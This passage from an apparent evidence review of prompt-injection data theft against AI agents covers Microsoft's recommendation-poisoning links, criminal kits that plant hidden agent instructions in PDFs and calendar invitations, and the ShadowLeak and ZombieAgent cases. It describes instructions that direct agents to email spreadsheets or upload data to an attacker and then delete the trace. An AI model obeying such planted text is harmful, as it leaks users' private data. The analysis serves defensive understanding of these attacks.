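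Microsoft reviewed AI-related links in email traffic over 60 days and found 50 different prompts of this kind, from 31 companies. All 31 were real businesses seeking promotion, including some in health and finance. Free tools for making the buttons helped the practice spread. The OECD's *Microsoft Warns of Widespread AI Recommendation Poisoning Attacks* (2026), another AI-generated entry, misreports the number of companies as more than 50.

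Microsoft didn't report how many people clicked or how many assistants saved the instruction. It wrote that the effect varied between assistants and over time, and that several behaviours reported earlier no longer occurred.

People are using links to manipulate AI assistants, but these links insert a company's text rather than send out private data, so OpenAI's check on outgoing addresses doesn't protect against them. Someone could use the same method to plant more harmful instructions. ZombieAgent, for example, used ChatGPT's memory to make the assistant collect sensitive information.

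### Tools for sale

Some criminals do want the data. Proofpoint's *Notes from Underground*, published in July 2026, describes tools sold in closed criminal forums, with subscriptions from about $150 a month. The tools produce emails, PDFs, calendar invitations and web pages containing hidden instructions for AI agents.

One sample PDF contained instructions for an agent to send every spreadsheet to an email address. A check on web addresses would not stop this. A sample calendar invitation contained instructions for the agent to upload data to a location the attacker controlled, then delete the instructions. The invitation appeared in the victim's calendar automatically, before the victim accepted it.

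Proofpoint, another security company, had not seen criminals use hidden instructions like these regularly or on a large scale. It suspects criminals have little reason to change their methods while ordinary scams aimed at people still work. The tools may not work well either. Proofpoint considered it debatable whether an agent would process the instruction in the PDF, because of where the seller had placed it.

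### Why a theft could go unnoticed

Varonis reported no exploitation of the SearchLeak flaw before disclosure, and Parameter reported no use of its ChatGPT account takeover outside its own tests. These statements are weak evidence that no attacks occurred, because outside researchers can't see the records of the company that runs the product.

If a criminal had used ShadowLeak against a company before OpenAI fixed it, OpenAI's servers would have sent the stolen data, so the company's network would have had no record of the request. The employee could have received a normal answer. The hostile email might still have been in the inbox, but nobody would have had a reason to reread it. Only OpenAI and the attacker could have known which address the agent opened.

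Even OpenAI would have needed to know what to look for to notice such an attack. Agents open web pages all the time, and an address containing Base64 or a series of visits to public pages might not stand out. A victim might later be burgled or lose control of an account without ever connecting it to a question they had asked ChatGPT.

Leaks are easier to trace when the user's browser sends the data, as in the image attacks, because an employer that keeps network logs could find the request afterwards. Scans would probably also detect a crude attack repeated across thousands of public pages. The lack of known victims is therefore some evidence against a large campaign of that sort, but it doesn't rule out a few targeted thefts.

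In November 2025, OpenAI said it had "not yet seen significant adoption" of prompt injection by attackers. That statement carries more weight than an outsider's would, because the companies that run the agents are in the best position to know whether such attacks are happening. But OpenAI gave no figures, and the statement predates the 2026 measurements.

### Is the danger growing?

Researchers are disclosing many attacks. In *AI agent security*, Constantin (2026) reported in July that four research teams had broken AI agents in four different ways within ten days. The number of disclosures partly reflects how many people are looking for flaws, and companies often fix a flaw before the public hears of it.

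Exposure has very likely grown too, because an attacker can steal more from an agent connected to its user's email and files. None of these studies measures how many people have connected an agent this way.

There is less evidence about attempted attacks. Google found 32 percent more malicious injections in Common Crawl in February 2026 than in November 2025. These include destructive commands as well as attempts to steal data. Without the totals, we can't tell whether the number rose from 25 to 33 or from 2,500 to 3,300. Google expects attacks to become more common and more sophisticated as agents grow more capable and attackers automate their work.

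Khodayari and colleagues looked up older copies of the Common Crawl pages on which they had found injections. Of the pages with a copy from a year earlier, 66 percent already contained an injection. The total may have grown by less than the 50 percent this implies, because the researchers started with pages that had an injection in October 2025 and couldn't count any that had lost theirs by then. Removal seems to be common. In January 2026, they rechecked the injections placed in the ordinary content of pages, and about a third had gone.

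News reports can also make older activity look new. In July, Mascellino (2026) covered Zscaler's findings in *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* and wrote that attackers "have begun" hiding instructions in websites, but Unit 42 had already listed one of the same scammer's sites in March.

The measurements published since January show people trying to manipulate AI systems, mostly for purposes other than stealing data. None of these studies counted successful data thefts, so they don't show whether theft through links is rising. Rolfe's claim that attackers are "increasingly exploiting" the way agents follow links therefore still lacks evidence.
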